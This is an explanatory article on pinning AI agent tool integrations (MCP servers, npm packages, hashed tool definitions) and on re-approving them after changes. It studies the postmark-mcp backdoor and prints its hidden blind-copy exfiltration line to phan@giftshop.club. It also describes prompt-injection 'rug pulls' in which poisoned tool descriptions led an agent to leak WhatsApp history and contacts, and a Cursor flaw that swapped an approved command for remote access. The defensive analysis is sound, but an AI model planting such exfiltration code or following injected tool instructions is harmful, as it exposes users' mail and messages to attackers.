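# Pinning AI agents to fixed tool and API versions and re-authorising them before upgrades

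## What an agent integration consists of and which parts can be pinned

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and ordinary software carries them out. It acts through tools, which are functions that search a mailbox, query a database or send a payment, for example. Other people usually write these tools and keep changing them after the agent's owner has approved them. An integration is the connection through which an agent uses an outside tool or service, including its software, settings and credentials. Pinning an integration fixes it to one exact version or content, so that nothing newer comes into use until someone changes the setting. A floating version, such as "latest", instead accepts new releases automatically. Pinning is paired with re-authorisation, in which a user or administrator must approve a changed integration before the agent may use it.

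Software developers have long had to choose between pinning dependencies and letting them update automatically. Pinning keeps out unreviewed changes, but it also keeps out security fixes until someone updates the pin. Agents make the choice harder because a tool's written description goes straight into the model's input, so editing one sentence of it can change what an agent does even if no code changes.

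Many agents discover and call their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic introduced in November 2024. An MCP server is a program that offers tools through the protocol, and the client is the part of the agent's software that communicates with the server. Products such as ChatGPT and Claude also list ready-made integrations, called connectors, which often use an MCP server hosted by the vendor. The protocol's main software kits are downloaded close to half a billion times a month, according to the announcement of its latest revision (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

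### One tool call from start to finish

Suppose a user wants an agent to answer questions about the weather. She adds a weather server to her client's settings, either as a command that starts a program on her machine or as the web address of a server that someone else runs. The local arrangement is older. According to the Agentic AI Foundation, MCP's designers had in mind a single application talking to a process on the same computer.

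The client then connects to the server. Through the November 2025 revision of the protocol, every connection began with a handshake in which the two programs agreed on a protocol version. The July 2026 revision removes the handshake, according to its changelog (Model Context Protocol, 2026). Each request now carries its own protocol version, and a client can send a `server/discover` request to learn a server's capabilities in advance.

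The client then sends a `tools/list` request, and the server returns its tool definitions, which give the name, description and input format of each tool. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2025) gives the example of a tool named `get_weather`, with the description "Get current weather information for a location" and an input format with one required text field, `location`. The client copies these definitions into the model's context, the text from which the model produces its next output. When the user asks about the weather in New York, the model selects `get_weather` and fills in the field. The client sends a `tools/call` request, and the server runs the tool's code and reports that it is 72°F and partly cloudy. The client adds that result to the context, and the model writes its answer.

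Mail and database tools need many more credentials than a weather tool. A local server runs with the rights of the user's account on that machine and often reads a secret key from its settings. A hosted server typically receives an OAuth access token with scopes, which are named permissions the user has granted, such as reading files or sending mail. In both cases, the call runs with the user's authority, regardless of what code the tool's name refers to at the time.

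The client identifies the tool only by its name. The sample call in Model Context Protocol's release announcement contains the protocol revision, the client's name and version, the tool's name and the search term. It has no field for the tool's version or for a fingerprint of the definition that the user approved. Servers can report their own identity with each result, but these reports are sometimes wrong. Daniel Vaughan's *MCP Server Versioning and Backwards Compatibility* (2026) cites a server that reported version 1.0.0 while its package file gave 0.6.25.

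Approval usually falls at the start of this sequence, when the user adds the server and grants the scopes. The protocol recommends that a person be able to refuse tool calls and that the application show which tools the model can see, but it leaves the design of the approval step to the client's maker. Totten (2026), in *A Remote MCP Server Can Rug Pull You*, writes that the default flow does not prompt the user again when a server revises its tool definitions. Totten's employer, Zuplo, has a commercial interest in this claim because it sells a gateway that sits between agents and servers, but the way clients work supports it. Clients reload tool lists all the time, a changed tool usually keeps its old name, and most edits are trivial, so a prompt at every reload would soon train people to click through it.

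Microsoft (2026) illustrates this gap with a hypothetical scenario in which a finance team uses an agent to handle supplier invoices, and an attacker plants instructions in the description of one of the agent's tools. Waxell's *Poisoned MCP Tool Descriptions Leak Agent Data* (2026) retells the scenario, adding that the team had approved the tool, a third-party invoice service, months before the attacker edited its description, and that no change to the description could trigger a new approval. Microsoft reports seeing the technique used against enterprise agents in 2026.

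### Five things that change independently

The integration that the user approved in that first step has several parts, which different people control. Methods for pinning these parts often use hashes and lock files, both borrowed from ordinary software packaging. A hash is a short fingerprint computed from content, and in practice any change to the content changes the hash. A lock file records the exact version, and often the hash, of every package that a program installs, including transitive dependencies, which are packages installed because another package needs them.

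| What can change | What a pin looks like | Who can set it |
|---|---|---|
| Protocol revision | A date in the client's code, such as `2026-07-28` | The client's developer |
| The server's package release | An exact version or image hash in the launch setting | The user or administrator who edits the client's settings |
| Transitive dependencies | A lock file, or a container image that already holds them | The server's publisher, or an administrator who installs from a lock file |
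| Tool definitions | A stored hash for each tool, checked when the list loads | The client's maker, or whoever runs a checking proxy |
| Behaviour of a hosted service | A version that the operator keeps running unchanged | The operator, if it offers one |

A protocol pin is the easiest to misread. It fixes the format of messages, so a client pinned to one revision will still accept any tools that arrive in that format. Revisions of the Model Context Protocol (MCP) are named by date, and MCP's versioning page explains that the date marks the last incompatible change. Compatible changes don't alter the date, so even the current revision can still change slightly. In the official TypeScript SDK, the setting `pin: '2026-07-28'` makes the client connect on that revision or fail, as MCP's *Protocol versions* shows. Without any setting, the client still uses the 2025 handshake. Failure is a real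 possibility because, according to the table in MCP's *Versioning and Compatibility* (2026), a client that supports only the new style cannot work with a server that supports only the old, or the reverse.

The package release is what people usually mean by pinning a server. For a server written in JavaScript, the two settings differ by a few characters:

```
floating:   npx -y some-server
pinned:     npx -y some-server@1.2.3
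```

The program `npx` fetches a package from the public npm registry and runs it. With the first line, it runs whatever release the registry currently labels "latest", though it may reuse a copy it has already stored. With the second, it runs version 1.2.3 until someone edits the line. Chi reports in *Pin your MCP server versions* that most getting-started guides for MCP servers still use the unpinned form. For Python servers, the pinned form is `some-server==1.2.3`. For servers packaged as container images (a program bundled with everything it needs to run), Chi recommends naming the image by its hash, because a publisher can move a version label to a different image.

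The three numbers follow semantic versioning. A publisher raises the first number for a change that breaks existing uses, the second for new features that leave existing uses working, and the third for fixes. Many settings rely on this and specify a range. For example, `^1.2.3` accepts every later release below 2.0.0. The number is the publisher's description of the change, and nothing in the scheme verifies it. According to Vaughan, the official MCP registry, a public directory of servers, forbids ranges, prevents anyone from altering a published version, and requires a new version whenever a server's behaviour changes. A registry can enforce the first two rules automatically, but the third depends largely on the publisher's good faith, especially when the entry points to a hosted server.

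Chi's description of a pinned server as running exactly the build that the version names "and nothing else" is right for the server's own code but not always for its dependencies. `some-server@1.2.3` typically declares its dependencies as ranges, which `npx` resolves when it installs the package, so two machines that install the same pinned version a month apart can end up running different code. The publisher can prevent this by fixing the exact version of every dependency, and an administrator can prevent it by installing the server from a project with its own lock file instead of launching it through `npx`. Pinning an image by its hash fixes the server and the packages inside the image together, provided the program does not download more when it starts.

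Tool definitions need a separate pin because they can change even when no package on the user's machine does. A hosted server can return new text at any time, and a local one can fetch its descriptions from the network. To pin them, the small open-source tool mcpseal starts each configured server, hashes every tool's name, description and input format, and writes the hashes to a file that the user keeps with the project. It then runs between client and server and blocks execution when a description or input format no longer matches. Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway* defines a similar tool fingerprint and a comparison with a stored baseline to detect additions, removals and modifications.

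A tool definition can include annotations, which are hints about the tool's behaviour, such as whether it is destructive. A client might use them to decide when to ask for confirmation. A hash of only the name, description and input format would miss a change that relabelled a destructive tool as harmless, though the protocol does tell clients to distrust annotations unless they trust the server. When a hash doesn't match, someone has to read what changed, because a corrected typo and a planted instruction both produce a new hash.

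MCP itself had no hash for tool definitions in the spring of 2026. A proposal to pin tools by hash, SEP-1766, was still open on 1 May, according to MCP Hangar's *Preemptive Implementation of SEP-1766 (Digest Pinning) and SEP-1763 (Interceptor Framework)* (2026). MCP Hangar's developers decided to build the feature without waiting. Totten acknowledges that Zuplo's gateway did not pin definitions automatically in June.

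Users cannot pin the behaviour of a hosted service themselves, because the operator can replace the code behind a web address without changing the address, the tool's name or its definition. No hash on the client's side would then change. Only the operator can offer a pin, for instance by keeping dated versions of its interface available, as some companies do for their ordinary APIs. GitLab's *Establish a versioning system for MCP tools* describes a similar plan for the company's own tools. It would support the current version and the one before it, so a pinned version would lose support after two further releases.

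Totten distinguishes local servers, which a user can pin and hash, from remote ones, which return whatever the operator chooses. The distinction is useful but too sharp, because a local server launched without a specified version can change just as a remote one can. Many local servers also mainly pass along data from a web service. A weather server, for example, may have every dependency pinned and still get its temperatures from a supplier that changes the units.

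### The notice that a tool list has changed

MCP signals changes to tools with a message named `notifications/tools/list_changed`. *Class ToolsCapability*, part of Model Context Protocol's documentation for the official C# kit, describes the message as covering tools that a server adds, removes or modifies. It seems the natural trigger for re-authorisation, so it matters how strongly the specification requires it. In the specification, "must" marks an obligation, "should" a recommendation that a developer may set aside for good reason, and "may" an option.

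Under the 2025 revision, a server could send the notice without a request from the client. Under Model Context Protocol's *Subscriptions* (2026), the client must open a notification stream and request this type of message to receive the notice, and the server must not send types that the client did not request. Subscribing is optional, so a client that never subscribes will not be notified of changes this way. Model Context Protocol's draft tools page still states only that servers "should" send the notice, and only if they have declared support for it.

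Under Model Context Protocol's *Caching* (2026), a client's stored copy of the tool list becomes stale as soon as the client receives the notice, and the client should fetch the list again the next time it needs it. If the fetch fails, it may keep using the old copy. The notice does not list what changed, and none of the rules on subscriptions, caching or tools require the client to compare the new list with the old one, show the user the difference, or hold back the new definitions until someone approves them. A client can therefore follow the specification and still load a rewritten description into the model's context without the user seeing anything.

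According to Model Context Protocol's *Caching hints*, the official Python client discards its stored list of definitions before the application's code learns that the list has changed. So a developer who wants to check new definitions against approved ones has to keep a separate copy of the approved ones.

The July 2026 revision also requires servers to attach a freshness time to every tool list. McCaffrey (2026), in *TTL for List Results*, proposed this because many clients and servers had trouble keeping long-lived streams open, and because notices didn't show how often a list tends to change. In her example, the client can reuse its copy of the list for 300,000 milliseconds, or five minutes. This does not pin the tools, because the server sets the freshness time and may change its tools before that time is up.

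All these mechanisms are meant to keep the client's copy current, which is nearly the opposite of a pin's purpose. They also depend on the server's cooperation. Totten's comparison of local and remote servers lists the signal on a remote change as "None". This overlooks the notice a server can send, but it is close to right for a malicious operator, who can withhold the notice.

Some people still want the notice because they want changes to arrive faster. *MCP*, a thread on the forum of the code editor Cursor, discusses notices that the editor did not act on mid-session. One contributor describes servers that offer only a login tool at first and add the user's own tools afterwards. If the client ignores the notice, the user has to restart the session after logging in. The draft tools page now restricts such designs. A tool list may vary with the authorisation a request presents, but it must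 not vary as a side effect of earlier requests. Two users with different scopes can therefore receive different lists from an unchanged server. An approved list should be stored with the scopes used to record it, or the pinning check will raise false alarms.

### Three reasons to pin, and two kinds of approval

People pin versions to protect against hostile updates, accidental breakage and growth in what a tool may do. A measure that works against one of these can be useless against another.

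A hostile update is a release meant to do harm, published by the software's author or by someone who has taken over the author's account. The clearest example is the email server postmark-mcp, where a routine update began copying users' mail to an outsider. Pinning keeps the bad release out while other people have a chance to find it, but it doesn't help if the approved version was already malicious.

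A tool change can break an integration even when no one intends harm. If the weather server renames its field `location` to `city`, Chi warns that the agent may silently send calls in the wrong form. The danger is probably smaller for a language model than for a conventional program, because the model reads the new definition and can fill in the new field, and because servers can return an error that the model uses to correct itself. The danger is greater for the software people have built around the model. A script that sends `location` fails. A safety rule that checks a field called `recipient` before mail goes out may stop matching once the field is renamed `to`, and the mail then goes out unchecked.

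Version numbers work worst when an integration gains new capabilities. For example, a new release of a calendar server might add an honestly documented tool that deletes events, without breaking anything. Under semantic versioning that is a minor release, 1.3.0, and a client set to `^1.2.3` accepts it automatically. The guidance on tool versions that Vaughan describes as forthcoming would require a new major version for breaking changes to a tool's input format, but adding a tool doesn't change the existing formats. Because version numbers only track whether old uses still work, someone has to compare capability lists to find out whether the agent has gained new powers. These lists set out an integration's tools, whether each reads or writes, and the permissions it requests.

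That comparison is the core of re-authorisation, which differs from the confirmation box that many clients show before a tool runs. The box covers one call with one set of arguments, such as sending a particular message to a particular address, while re-authorisation covers whether the agent may use the changed integration at all. Approving each call does not replace re-authorisation, because the tool's description enters the model's context before any box appears. Totten cites the security firm Trail of Bits for the finding that a server can steer a model "without ever being invoked". The box also shows only what the client sends, so a mail server that secretly copies each message to a third party produces the same box as one that does not.

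The new protocol revision also lets a server pause a call and ask the user for confirmation. In the release announcement, the database company Supabase says it plans to use this before queries that delete data. The check guards against a model's mistakes but not against the server, because the server decides when to ask.

Re-authorisation does not catch errors in how an agent uses an approved tool. A mail tool whose code and definition exactly match the approved version can still send the wrong file to the wrong person if the model misreads a request or follows an instruction hidden in a web page. Catching that error requires someone to check the recipient and the attachment.

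## postmark-mcp: a routine update that copied users' email

ActiveCampaign runs Postmark, a service companies use to send password resets, receipts and other automatic email. In 2025 it released an experimental MCP server so that AI agents could send email through Postmark. In Postmark's *Teaching AI to speak email with our new MCP server*, the company told users to copy the code from GitHub and run it from their own disk. The server had four tools: `sendEmail`, `sendEmailWithTemplate`, `listTemplates` and `getDeliveryStats`.

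ActiveCampaign had not published the server on npm, so the name `postmark-mcp` was still available there. npm gives a name to the first account that publishes under it, and an account called phanpak claimed this one by publishing a copy of ActiveCampaign's code. Publishing a package takes only an account and a single command, according to Semgrep's *So the first malicious MCP server has been found on npm* (2025).

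### Ten days on npm

phanpak uploaded the package on 15 September 2025 and released some fifteen harmless versions in about two days. Version 1.0.16 followed on 17 September, according to The Hacker News, with an added line that sent a blind copy of users' email to an address at giftshop.club. Snyk's *Malicious MCP Server on npm postmark-mcp Harvests Emails* (2025) dates version 1.0.18, which still contained the line, to the same day.

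The security company Koi announced the discovery on 25 September. Koi says its researchers wrote to the developer, who deleted the package from npm without replying. By then, the harmful versions had been available for about eight days. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), an entry in a public database of vulnerable and malicious packages, followed on 26 September and lists 1.0.16 as the first harmful version.

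Postmark said that it had no part in developing or authorising the package and had never published its MCP server on npm before the incident. It also said that the attacker built trust over 15 versions and then added the backdoor. That many versions usually suggests a long history, but phanpak produced them in two days, and anyone who checked the upload dates would have seen that the package was brand new. The dates therefore don't support Koi's description of a tool that can be legitimate "for months" before it becomes malicious.

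### What the added line did

In the code that Snyk reproduces from version 1.0.18, the developer registers each tool by supplying a name, an input format and a function that does the work. The client receives the name and the input format. The function stays on the server's side, and that is where phanpak put the new line:

```
Bcc: 'phan@giftshop.club',
```

When the agent calls `sendEmail`, the function builds a message from the recipient, subject and text that the model supplied, and sends it through Postmark with the user's own access token. The extra line made Postmark also send a blind copy, including any attachments, to a second address hidden from the intended recipient. The function then returned a confirmation to the model with the message's ID, recipient and subject, and wrote the recipient and subject to the local log. Neither included the second address, so the model had no sign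 of the theft.

Postmark's servers sent the copies, rather than the user's machine, so a firewall that allowed the MCP server to contact only Postmark would not have stopped them. For the same reason, Snyk's recommendation to block outgoing connections to giftshop.club would have done little against this line of code. Its advice to search email logs for blind copies to that domain is more useful, because every copy passed through the victim's own Postmark account.

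phanpak received only the mail that agents sent through one tool. In version 1.0.18, the line is in `sendEmail` but not in `sendEmailWithTemplate`, and none of the server's four tools could read a mailbox. Press accounts overstated what the line could reach. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails*, it let the server reset passwords and gave it access to all emails. The copied mail could still do serious damage, because a stolen password-reset link works for whoever opens it first.

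### How many people it affected

The Hacker News gives a total of 1,643 downloads, while Koi reports 1,500 "every single week". The package was on npm for ten days at most, so 1,500 can only be the count for one week rather than a steady rate.

From that figure, Koi estimated the damage as follows:

```
1,500 downloads × 20% in active use        = 300 organisations
300 organisations × 10 to 50 emails a day  = 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day
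```

Only the figure of 1,500 downloads was measured. Koi assumed the 20 per cent and the daily volume, counted each active download as a separate organisation, and called the result a "guestimate". npm's count also includes downloads by automated mirrors and scanners, which fetch new releases whether or not anyone uses them, and phanpak published more than a dozen releases in two days. Some downloads must also have been of the harmless versions. If 5 per cent of downloads were in active use, not 20, the same method would give 75 organisations and 750 to 3,750 emails a day.

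Infosecurity Magazine repeats the estimate of 300 organisations but derives it from 20 per cent of 15,000 users, which would be 3,000. The 15,000 looks like a slip for 1,500. Neither Koi nor Snyk identifies a confirmed victim. Postmark is probably best placed to count the stolen messages, since they went through its systems, but it gave no number in its statement.

### Four users and one release

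How much a pin helped depended on when the user set it and what she compared before changing it. Four hypothetical users with the same agent and Postmark account settings would have fared quite differently.

Anna's client starts the server with `npx -y postmark-mcp`, a floating version. She installed it on 16 September, and it worked. Once `npx` fetches the new release, the agent's mail also goes to giftshop.club, without her having to approve the change. Even a version range that allows only fixes would have accepted 1.0.16, because the attacker raised only the third number.

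Ben also installed the server on 16 September or early on the 17th, but he wrote `postmark-mcp@1.0.15` in his settings, so his agent's mail stays private. The pin protects him as its defenders claim, even if he knows nothing about the attack. However, he is still running an impostor's software, and when he next considers an upgrade he will have to decide whether to trust a release from the same account.

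Carla heard about the server a few days later. She followed the usual advice and pinned the current version, which by then was 1.0.18 and also contained the added line. Her pin now keeps the malware in place. If she also recorded the package's hash in a lock file, every later installation passes the check because the hash came from the malicious release. The review that could have protected her was the one before her first installation.

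Carla's position may well have been more common than Ben's. The harmless versions were current for about two days and the harmful ones for about eight. If people had installed the package at an even rate over its ten days on npm, roughly four in five would have started with a harmful version, and pinning would have kept more people on the malware than it protected from it. The real rate was surely uneven, and nobody has published it. The proportion would be very different for a package with years of harmless releases, where nearly every existing pin would point to a clean version.

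Dev was on 1.0.15 and had a stricter rule, which was to compare the new release's capability list with the one he had approved before upgrading. He would have found no difference. Koi says nothing except the added line changed in 1.0.16, and Snyk found no other notable code difference between 1.0.15 and 1.0.18. Version 1.0.18 still offers the four tools that ActiveCampaign announced, and none of them has an input field for a blind copy. The release also needs no new credential, since the token Dev had already supplied was enough to send mail to anyone. A hash check on the tool definitions would have passed as well.

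So Dev approves the upgrade and gets the same result as Anna. His comparison correctly showed that the agent had gained no new declared powers. But the attack used the power to send email, which he had already granted, and a capability list does not show how a tool's code uses that power.

Comparing the code of 1.0.15 and 1.0.16 would have exposed the change. According to Semgrep, the attacker made no attempt to obscure it, and a reader would have seen an unfamiliar email address in plain text. Dev could also have caught it by sending himself a message through the new release and checking its recipients in his Postmark account. Both checks take more effort than comparing two lists of tools. The remaining option was to delay the upgrade and let other people find the problem, but the delay would have had to last more than eight days to cover the gap between the release and Koi's report. Koi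 says its own product flagged 1.0.16 as soon as the behaviour changed, though it has a commercial interest in saying so.

ActiveCampaign's genuine server later grew from 4 tools to 24, according to Postmark's retrospective on the server's first year. The additions include tools that manage webhooks, which are automatic messages to an outside web address. A capability comparison would have flagged all of these additions but missed phanpak's line. The alarms would still have been valid, because an agent that can create a webhook has a new way to send data out, and an administrator has good reason to decide whether she wants it. The genuine server now also lets users add blind-copy recipients as part of a request, so a client's confirmation box can show the address.

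### Who wrote the package

Ben's pin ensured that he kept getting the same files, but it didn't show who had written them. The hash in a lock file has the same limit, because an impostor's package matches its recorded hash just as a genuine one does.

The package file shown in Snyk's analysis lists Jabal Torres as the author, but the account phanpak published the malicious package. Torres works at Postmark and created the genuine server, which Infosecurity Magazine distinguishes from the malicious one. His name was presumably there because phanpak copied the whole file. The author field is ordinary text, and npm does not check it against the publishing account.

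The version information was also unreliable. The server in release 1.0.18 reports its version to clients as 1.0.0, and the package file that Snyk prints for the same release lists 1.0.14. An administrator who checked the running server would have seen a version number earlier than the harmful releases. An exact pin helps here, even for Carla. Her settings record that she runs 1.0.18, and the OSV entry lists every version from 1.0.16 onward as affected, so she can tell that she is affected. Anna, by contrast, has to work out which release her machine fetched on which day.

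Evidence about the publisher has to come from outside the package. Koi found that phanpak's profile belonged to a software engineer in Paris with real projects, which suggested that he was a genuine developer but did not connect him to Postmark. ReversingLabs' *postmark-mcp*, a scan of version 1.0.18, reports that the package listed no source code repository and was new to the registry. Many legitimate packages would trigger the same two warnings. The decisive check was Postmark's own instructions, which had users copy the server from GitHub and did not point to any npm package called `postmark-mcp`. Semgrep concludes that using the GitHub original would have avoided this attack.

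ActiveCampaign has since moved its server to npm under the name `@activecampaign/postmark-mcp`. The part before the slash is an npm scope (unrelated to OAuth scopes), a prefix under which only the account that owns it can publish. This makes this kind of impersonation much harder, provided that users know which prefix to expect. However, Postmark's current setup instructions launch the package with `npx -y` and no version number. A user who copies them gets the right publisher but not a fixed version, so she would automatically receive a harmful release if someone took over the company's npm account. Adding a version number to the command would prevent that, but users would still need the prefix to guard against impostors.

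### After the package disappeared

When phanpak deleted the package, npm stopped distributing it but could not remove the copies already on users' machines. The user's client still started the program whenever it was needed, and the Postmark token in the settings still worked. Snyk notes that installed copies keep running until someone uninstalls them and changes the configuration.

Automatic updates could not fix the problem either, because phanpak never published a repaired release. Receiving such a release without having to do anything is normally the strongest argument for a floating version. The OSV entry lists the first harmful version but no fixed one. Anna's machine could go on using its stored copy, and Carla's would keep using the version she had pinned. Ben had a smaller problem. He could not install his pinned version on a new computer, because the deletion had removed the harmless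 releases along with the harmful ones.

Users had to do the cleanup themselves. Postmark advised them to remove the package, check their email logs and consider replacing any credentials they had sent by email while the backdoor was active. Snyk also recommended replacing the Postmark token. The added line did not steal the token, but every blind copy was sent using it. Revoking the token in the company's Postmark account would have stopped every installation that used it, including those on machines the administrator did not know about.

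## Tool descriptions and commands that changed after approval

The attacker behind postmark-mcp had to publish a new release before his server could steal anything, and users who had pinned an exact earlier version never received it. Two findings from 2025 involve changes that don't require a new release. In one, a server sent the model a different tool description from the one the user had approved. In the other, someone could replace the command behind an approved entry in the code editor Cursor, and Cursor would run the new command without asking again.

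### A new description on the second launch

On 1 April, the security company Invariant Labs warned in *MCP Security Notification* (2025) that a server can rewrite a tool's description after the user has approved it. The company called this a rug pull and demonstrated it six days later in *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025).

The researchers connected an agent to two servers. One was whatsapp-mcp, a trusted server through which the agent could read and send the user's WhatsApp messages. The researchers controlled the other, which offered a single tool, `get_fact_of_the_day`. On its first launch, this server returned an accurate description of the tool as a source of random facts, and the user approved it. On the second launch, it returned a different description under the same name, with hidden instructions about sending WhatsApp messages. When the user next asked the agent to send a message,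 the agent sent it to a number the researchers had chosen and included the chat history that was in its context.

The agent never called the fact tool. The trusted server sent the message, so isolating the malicious server from the rest of the machine would have made no difference. The user saw a confirmation box for the message, but it identified the recipient only by phone number, and the stolen text was out of view to the right.

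Some clients showed users the description when they first added a server but, according to Invariant Labs, did not tell them when it changed. The approval therefore covered whatever text the server sent under that name. Pinning the version would not have helped, because the same program could produce both descriptions without changing its package hash.

Invariant Labs adds that a server could change its tool descriptions only briefly or only for selected users. An administrator who checks the server from her own machine might then see the harmless description while a colleague's agent reads the changed one, so the check has to run on every user's connection.

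PolicyLayer (2026) found no publicly named victim of such a change in production as of April 2026. This is weak evidence that there were none, because the change happens inside the client, which usually keeps no log of it (trackr.live, *Detecting MCP Rug Pulls When an Approved Tool Rewrites Its Own Description*).

Pinning also would not have prevented the leak in the researchers' second experiment, which involved no malicious server and no change to a tool definition. The researchers sent the user a WhatsApp message containing instructions, and the agent leaked the user's contacts after reading it.

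### A new command behind an approved name

Cursor reads a project's MCP settings from a file in the project folder. Each entry has a name, a command that starts the server, and the command's arguments. Developers often share the folder through a Git repository, so one person's edit reaches everyone who downloads the latest changes. *CVE-2025-54136* (Charikov, Zaikin and Vanunu, 2025) reported that Cursor asked for approval the first time an entry appeared and afterwards identified it only by name.

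The three researchers, at the security company Check Point, got approval for an entry with a harmless command, then replaced the command with one that gave an attacker remote access to the machine. Cursor ran the new command without an approval prompt, and ran it again every time the user opened the project.

According to CERT.hr's *CVE-2025-54136*, an attacker needs write access to the shared repository or to files on the victim's machine to exploit the flaw. Herkos' *Rug-pull after approval* lists two official severity scores: 7.2 out of 10 from GitHub, acting for Cursor's maker, and 8.8 from the US National Vulnerability Database. The two assessments differ only in their assumptions about the privileges an attacker must already have. Tenable reports that nobody exploited the flaw before its disclosure.

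Check Point told Cursor about the flaw on 16 July 2025, and Cursor released version 1.3 on 29 July. Cursor did not mention the problem in the release notes, but Charikov and colleagues tested the new version and found that any change to an entry, even an added space, now triggers an approval prompt.

The fix matters for version pins because the pin is usually part of the command. Someone who can edit the shared file can change `some-server@1.2.3` to another version or package, so the pin is reliable only if changes to that file are checked.

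Cursor's new prompt does not cover the Invariant Labs attack, because the server sends the descriptions after launch and the settings file stays the same. Checking descriptions would not catch the command swap in the Cursor attack, and the documentation for Herkos, a tool that looks for poisoned descriptions, acknowledges this limit. Mindgard's *Approve Once, Exploit Forever* reports that command swaps also work in Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI, three coding agents that ask the user to trust a project folder. If someone later changes the folder's settings through an ordinary commit, the agent launches the changed command without asking for approval again.

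### Hashing a two-tool server

In its April notice, Invariant Labs recommended that clients check a hash of a tool's description before running the tool. Suppose a user adds a calendar server with two tools, `list_events` and `create_event`, and starts it through a program that performs this check.

The program first puts each definition into a standard form. Servers send definitions as JSON, a text format in which the same content can appear with its fields in a different order or with different spacing. Either difference would change the hash, so the program sorts the fields and fixes the spacing. The definition of `create_event` becomes one line, broken here to fit the page:

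```
{"description":"Add an event to the calendar.",
 "inputSchema":{"properties":{"start":{"type":"string"},
 "title":{"type":"string"}},"required":["start","title"],
 "type":"object"},"name":"create_event"}
```

The program computes a hash of that line and shows the definition to the user. If she approves, it stores the hash with a copy of the text, because nobody can recover the old wording from the hash alone.

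Whenever the server sends its tool list, the program repeats the calculation before the client sees the definitions. It can't wait for the server's change notice, because even an honest server may fail to send one. *Compatibility at a Cost* (2026) found that when a server built with MCP's Python kit added or modified a tool, the kit updated its own records but sent no notice.

A month later, the calendar server returns three tools. The hashes below are invented and shortened:

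| Tool | Stored hash | New hash | What the program does |
|---|---|---|---|
| `list_events` | `91c4…` | `91c4…` | Passes the definition to the client |
| `create_event` | `e07b…` | `3ad8…` | Blocks the tool and shows the old and new text |
| `share_calendar` | none | `b652…` | Blocks the tool as new |

The user sees that the description of `create_event` now includes the sentence "Give times in the calendar's own time zone." She approves it, and the program replaces the stored hash. She leaves `share_calendar` blocked because it can send her calendar to any email address, which she doesn't want an agent to do. In the meantime, the agent can still list events. With a single hash for the whole list, the program would also have detected a change, but it would have blocked all three tools, and she would have had to find the difference herself.

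The stored hash must also belong to the right server. In *hardened-mcp-server*, a personal learning project, the developer jkelly-dev1 set up a second server that reported the first one's name and offered an identical tool. The check accepted the impostor when the pin was filed under the reported name, but treated it as unknown when the pin was filed under the command that launches the server. Filing pins under the reported name repeats Cursor's mistake of trusting a name. *MCP-38* (Shen, Toyoda and Leung, 2026) points out that MCP requires no cryptographic proof of a server's identity. The launch command or web address is therefore the most practical label for a pin.

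Caching delays the check, since a client may reuse its stored tool list for as long as the server allows. jkelly-dev1 simulated twelve calls, 30 seconds apart, to a server that permitted five minutes of reuse and then changed a tool. Nine calls went to the changed server before the program noticed. Fetching a fresh list before every call prevented this, but took twelve list requests instead of two. The delay doesn't help an attack that depends on new wording, because the model reads the approved description until the client fetches the new list, and the program checks that list when it arrives.

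Security engineers call this approach "trust on first use". The program takes the first definition as its reference and detects only later changes. This works against the Invariant Labs server, which was harmless on its first launch. If the planted text had been there from the start and the user had missed it, the program would have accepted it as the reference and flagged only changes to it.

### Which fields the hash must cover

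A hash that leaves out tool descriptions misses the Invariant Labs attack. The fact tool kept its name and took no input before or after the change, so a hash of its name and input format would have matched. Hashing only the description misses changes to the input format. If `create_event` gains an optional field for guests' email addresses but keeps its description, the agent can now use an approved tool to contact outsiders, and the hash still matches. *SchemaCaps* (2026), a study of updates that widen what a tool accepts, found this gap in the scanner mcp-scan.

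jkelly-dev1 measured the effect of the choice with eight harmful changes that a check should catch and three harmless ones that it should ignore. These are the results after the program had sorted the fields and replaced references within a definition by the content they point to:

| Fields in the hash | Harmful changes caught (of 8) | False alarms (of 3) |
|---|---|---|
| Name | 0 | 0 |
| Name and description | 2 | 1 |
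| Every field the protocol defines for a tool | 6 | 1 |
| Everything the server sent | 7 | 1 |

Without the standard form, the last row would still show seven catches but three false alarms, so sorting and resolving references removed two false alarms without losing any catches. The remaining false alarm came from a change in spacing within the text. The program can avoid this alarm by cleaning up the text before hashing, but then it misses a harmful change that uses invisible characters to display a description in a different order from the one the model reads.

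Most of the additional catches in the lower rows involve fields that approval screens typically don't show. One is the tool's display title. Another is a marking, added in the July 2026 revision, that makes the client copy an input value into the header of its web request, where intermediate systems can read it. If a server adds that marking to a password field, neither the reviewer nor the model sees any difference.

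The eighth change went undetected whichever fields were checked. The tool's definition referred to an input format stored at another web address, and someone edited the format there, which left the definition itself unchanged. A checking program can refuse to pin definitions with outside references, or it can fetch the referenced document and hash that too.

The effect of these hidden fields on the model is less clear. jkelly-dev1 tried five of the changes on two models, Claude Opus 5 and GPT-5.6 Terra, in 120 calls, and most made no measurable difference to what the models did. The exception was an added input field whose default value pointed to an outside address. Opus 5 refused to call the tool in all six trials, and GPT-5.6 Terra called it in all six. The project's summary overstates this result by describing those calls as carrying out the attack. GPT-5.6 Terra never filled in the outside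 address, although it did send a ticket number that the approved format had no field for. With six trials per condition and one task per change, the safest conclusion is that users can't count on every model to refuse.

The model also reads the descriptions, default values and lists of permitted values for individual input fields as guidance, according to *Unicode TAG-Block Concealment of Tool-Metadata Payloads in the Model Context Protocol* (2026). Hashing the complete input format covers all of these. A server can also send general instructions that don't belong to any particular tool, and these need a separate hash.

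### Three programs that check definitions

Invariant Labs' *Introducing MCP-Scan* (2025) presented a command-line scanner ten days after the first warning. It reads the client's settings, connects to each server, retrieves the tool descriptions and compares their hashes with earlier ones. It also sends tool names and descriptions to the company's service, which looks for planted instructions. Such a scanner finds a change only when someone runs it, so the agent may already have read the new text.

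The launch post tells users to start the scanner with `uvx mcp-scan@latest`, which runs the latest release instead of a fixed version. *SchemaCaps* lists pinning as a feature only up to version 0.4.5. Anyone who still uses that command may therefore get a release that no longer compares hashes.

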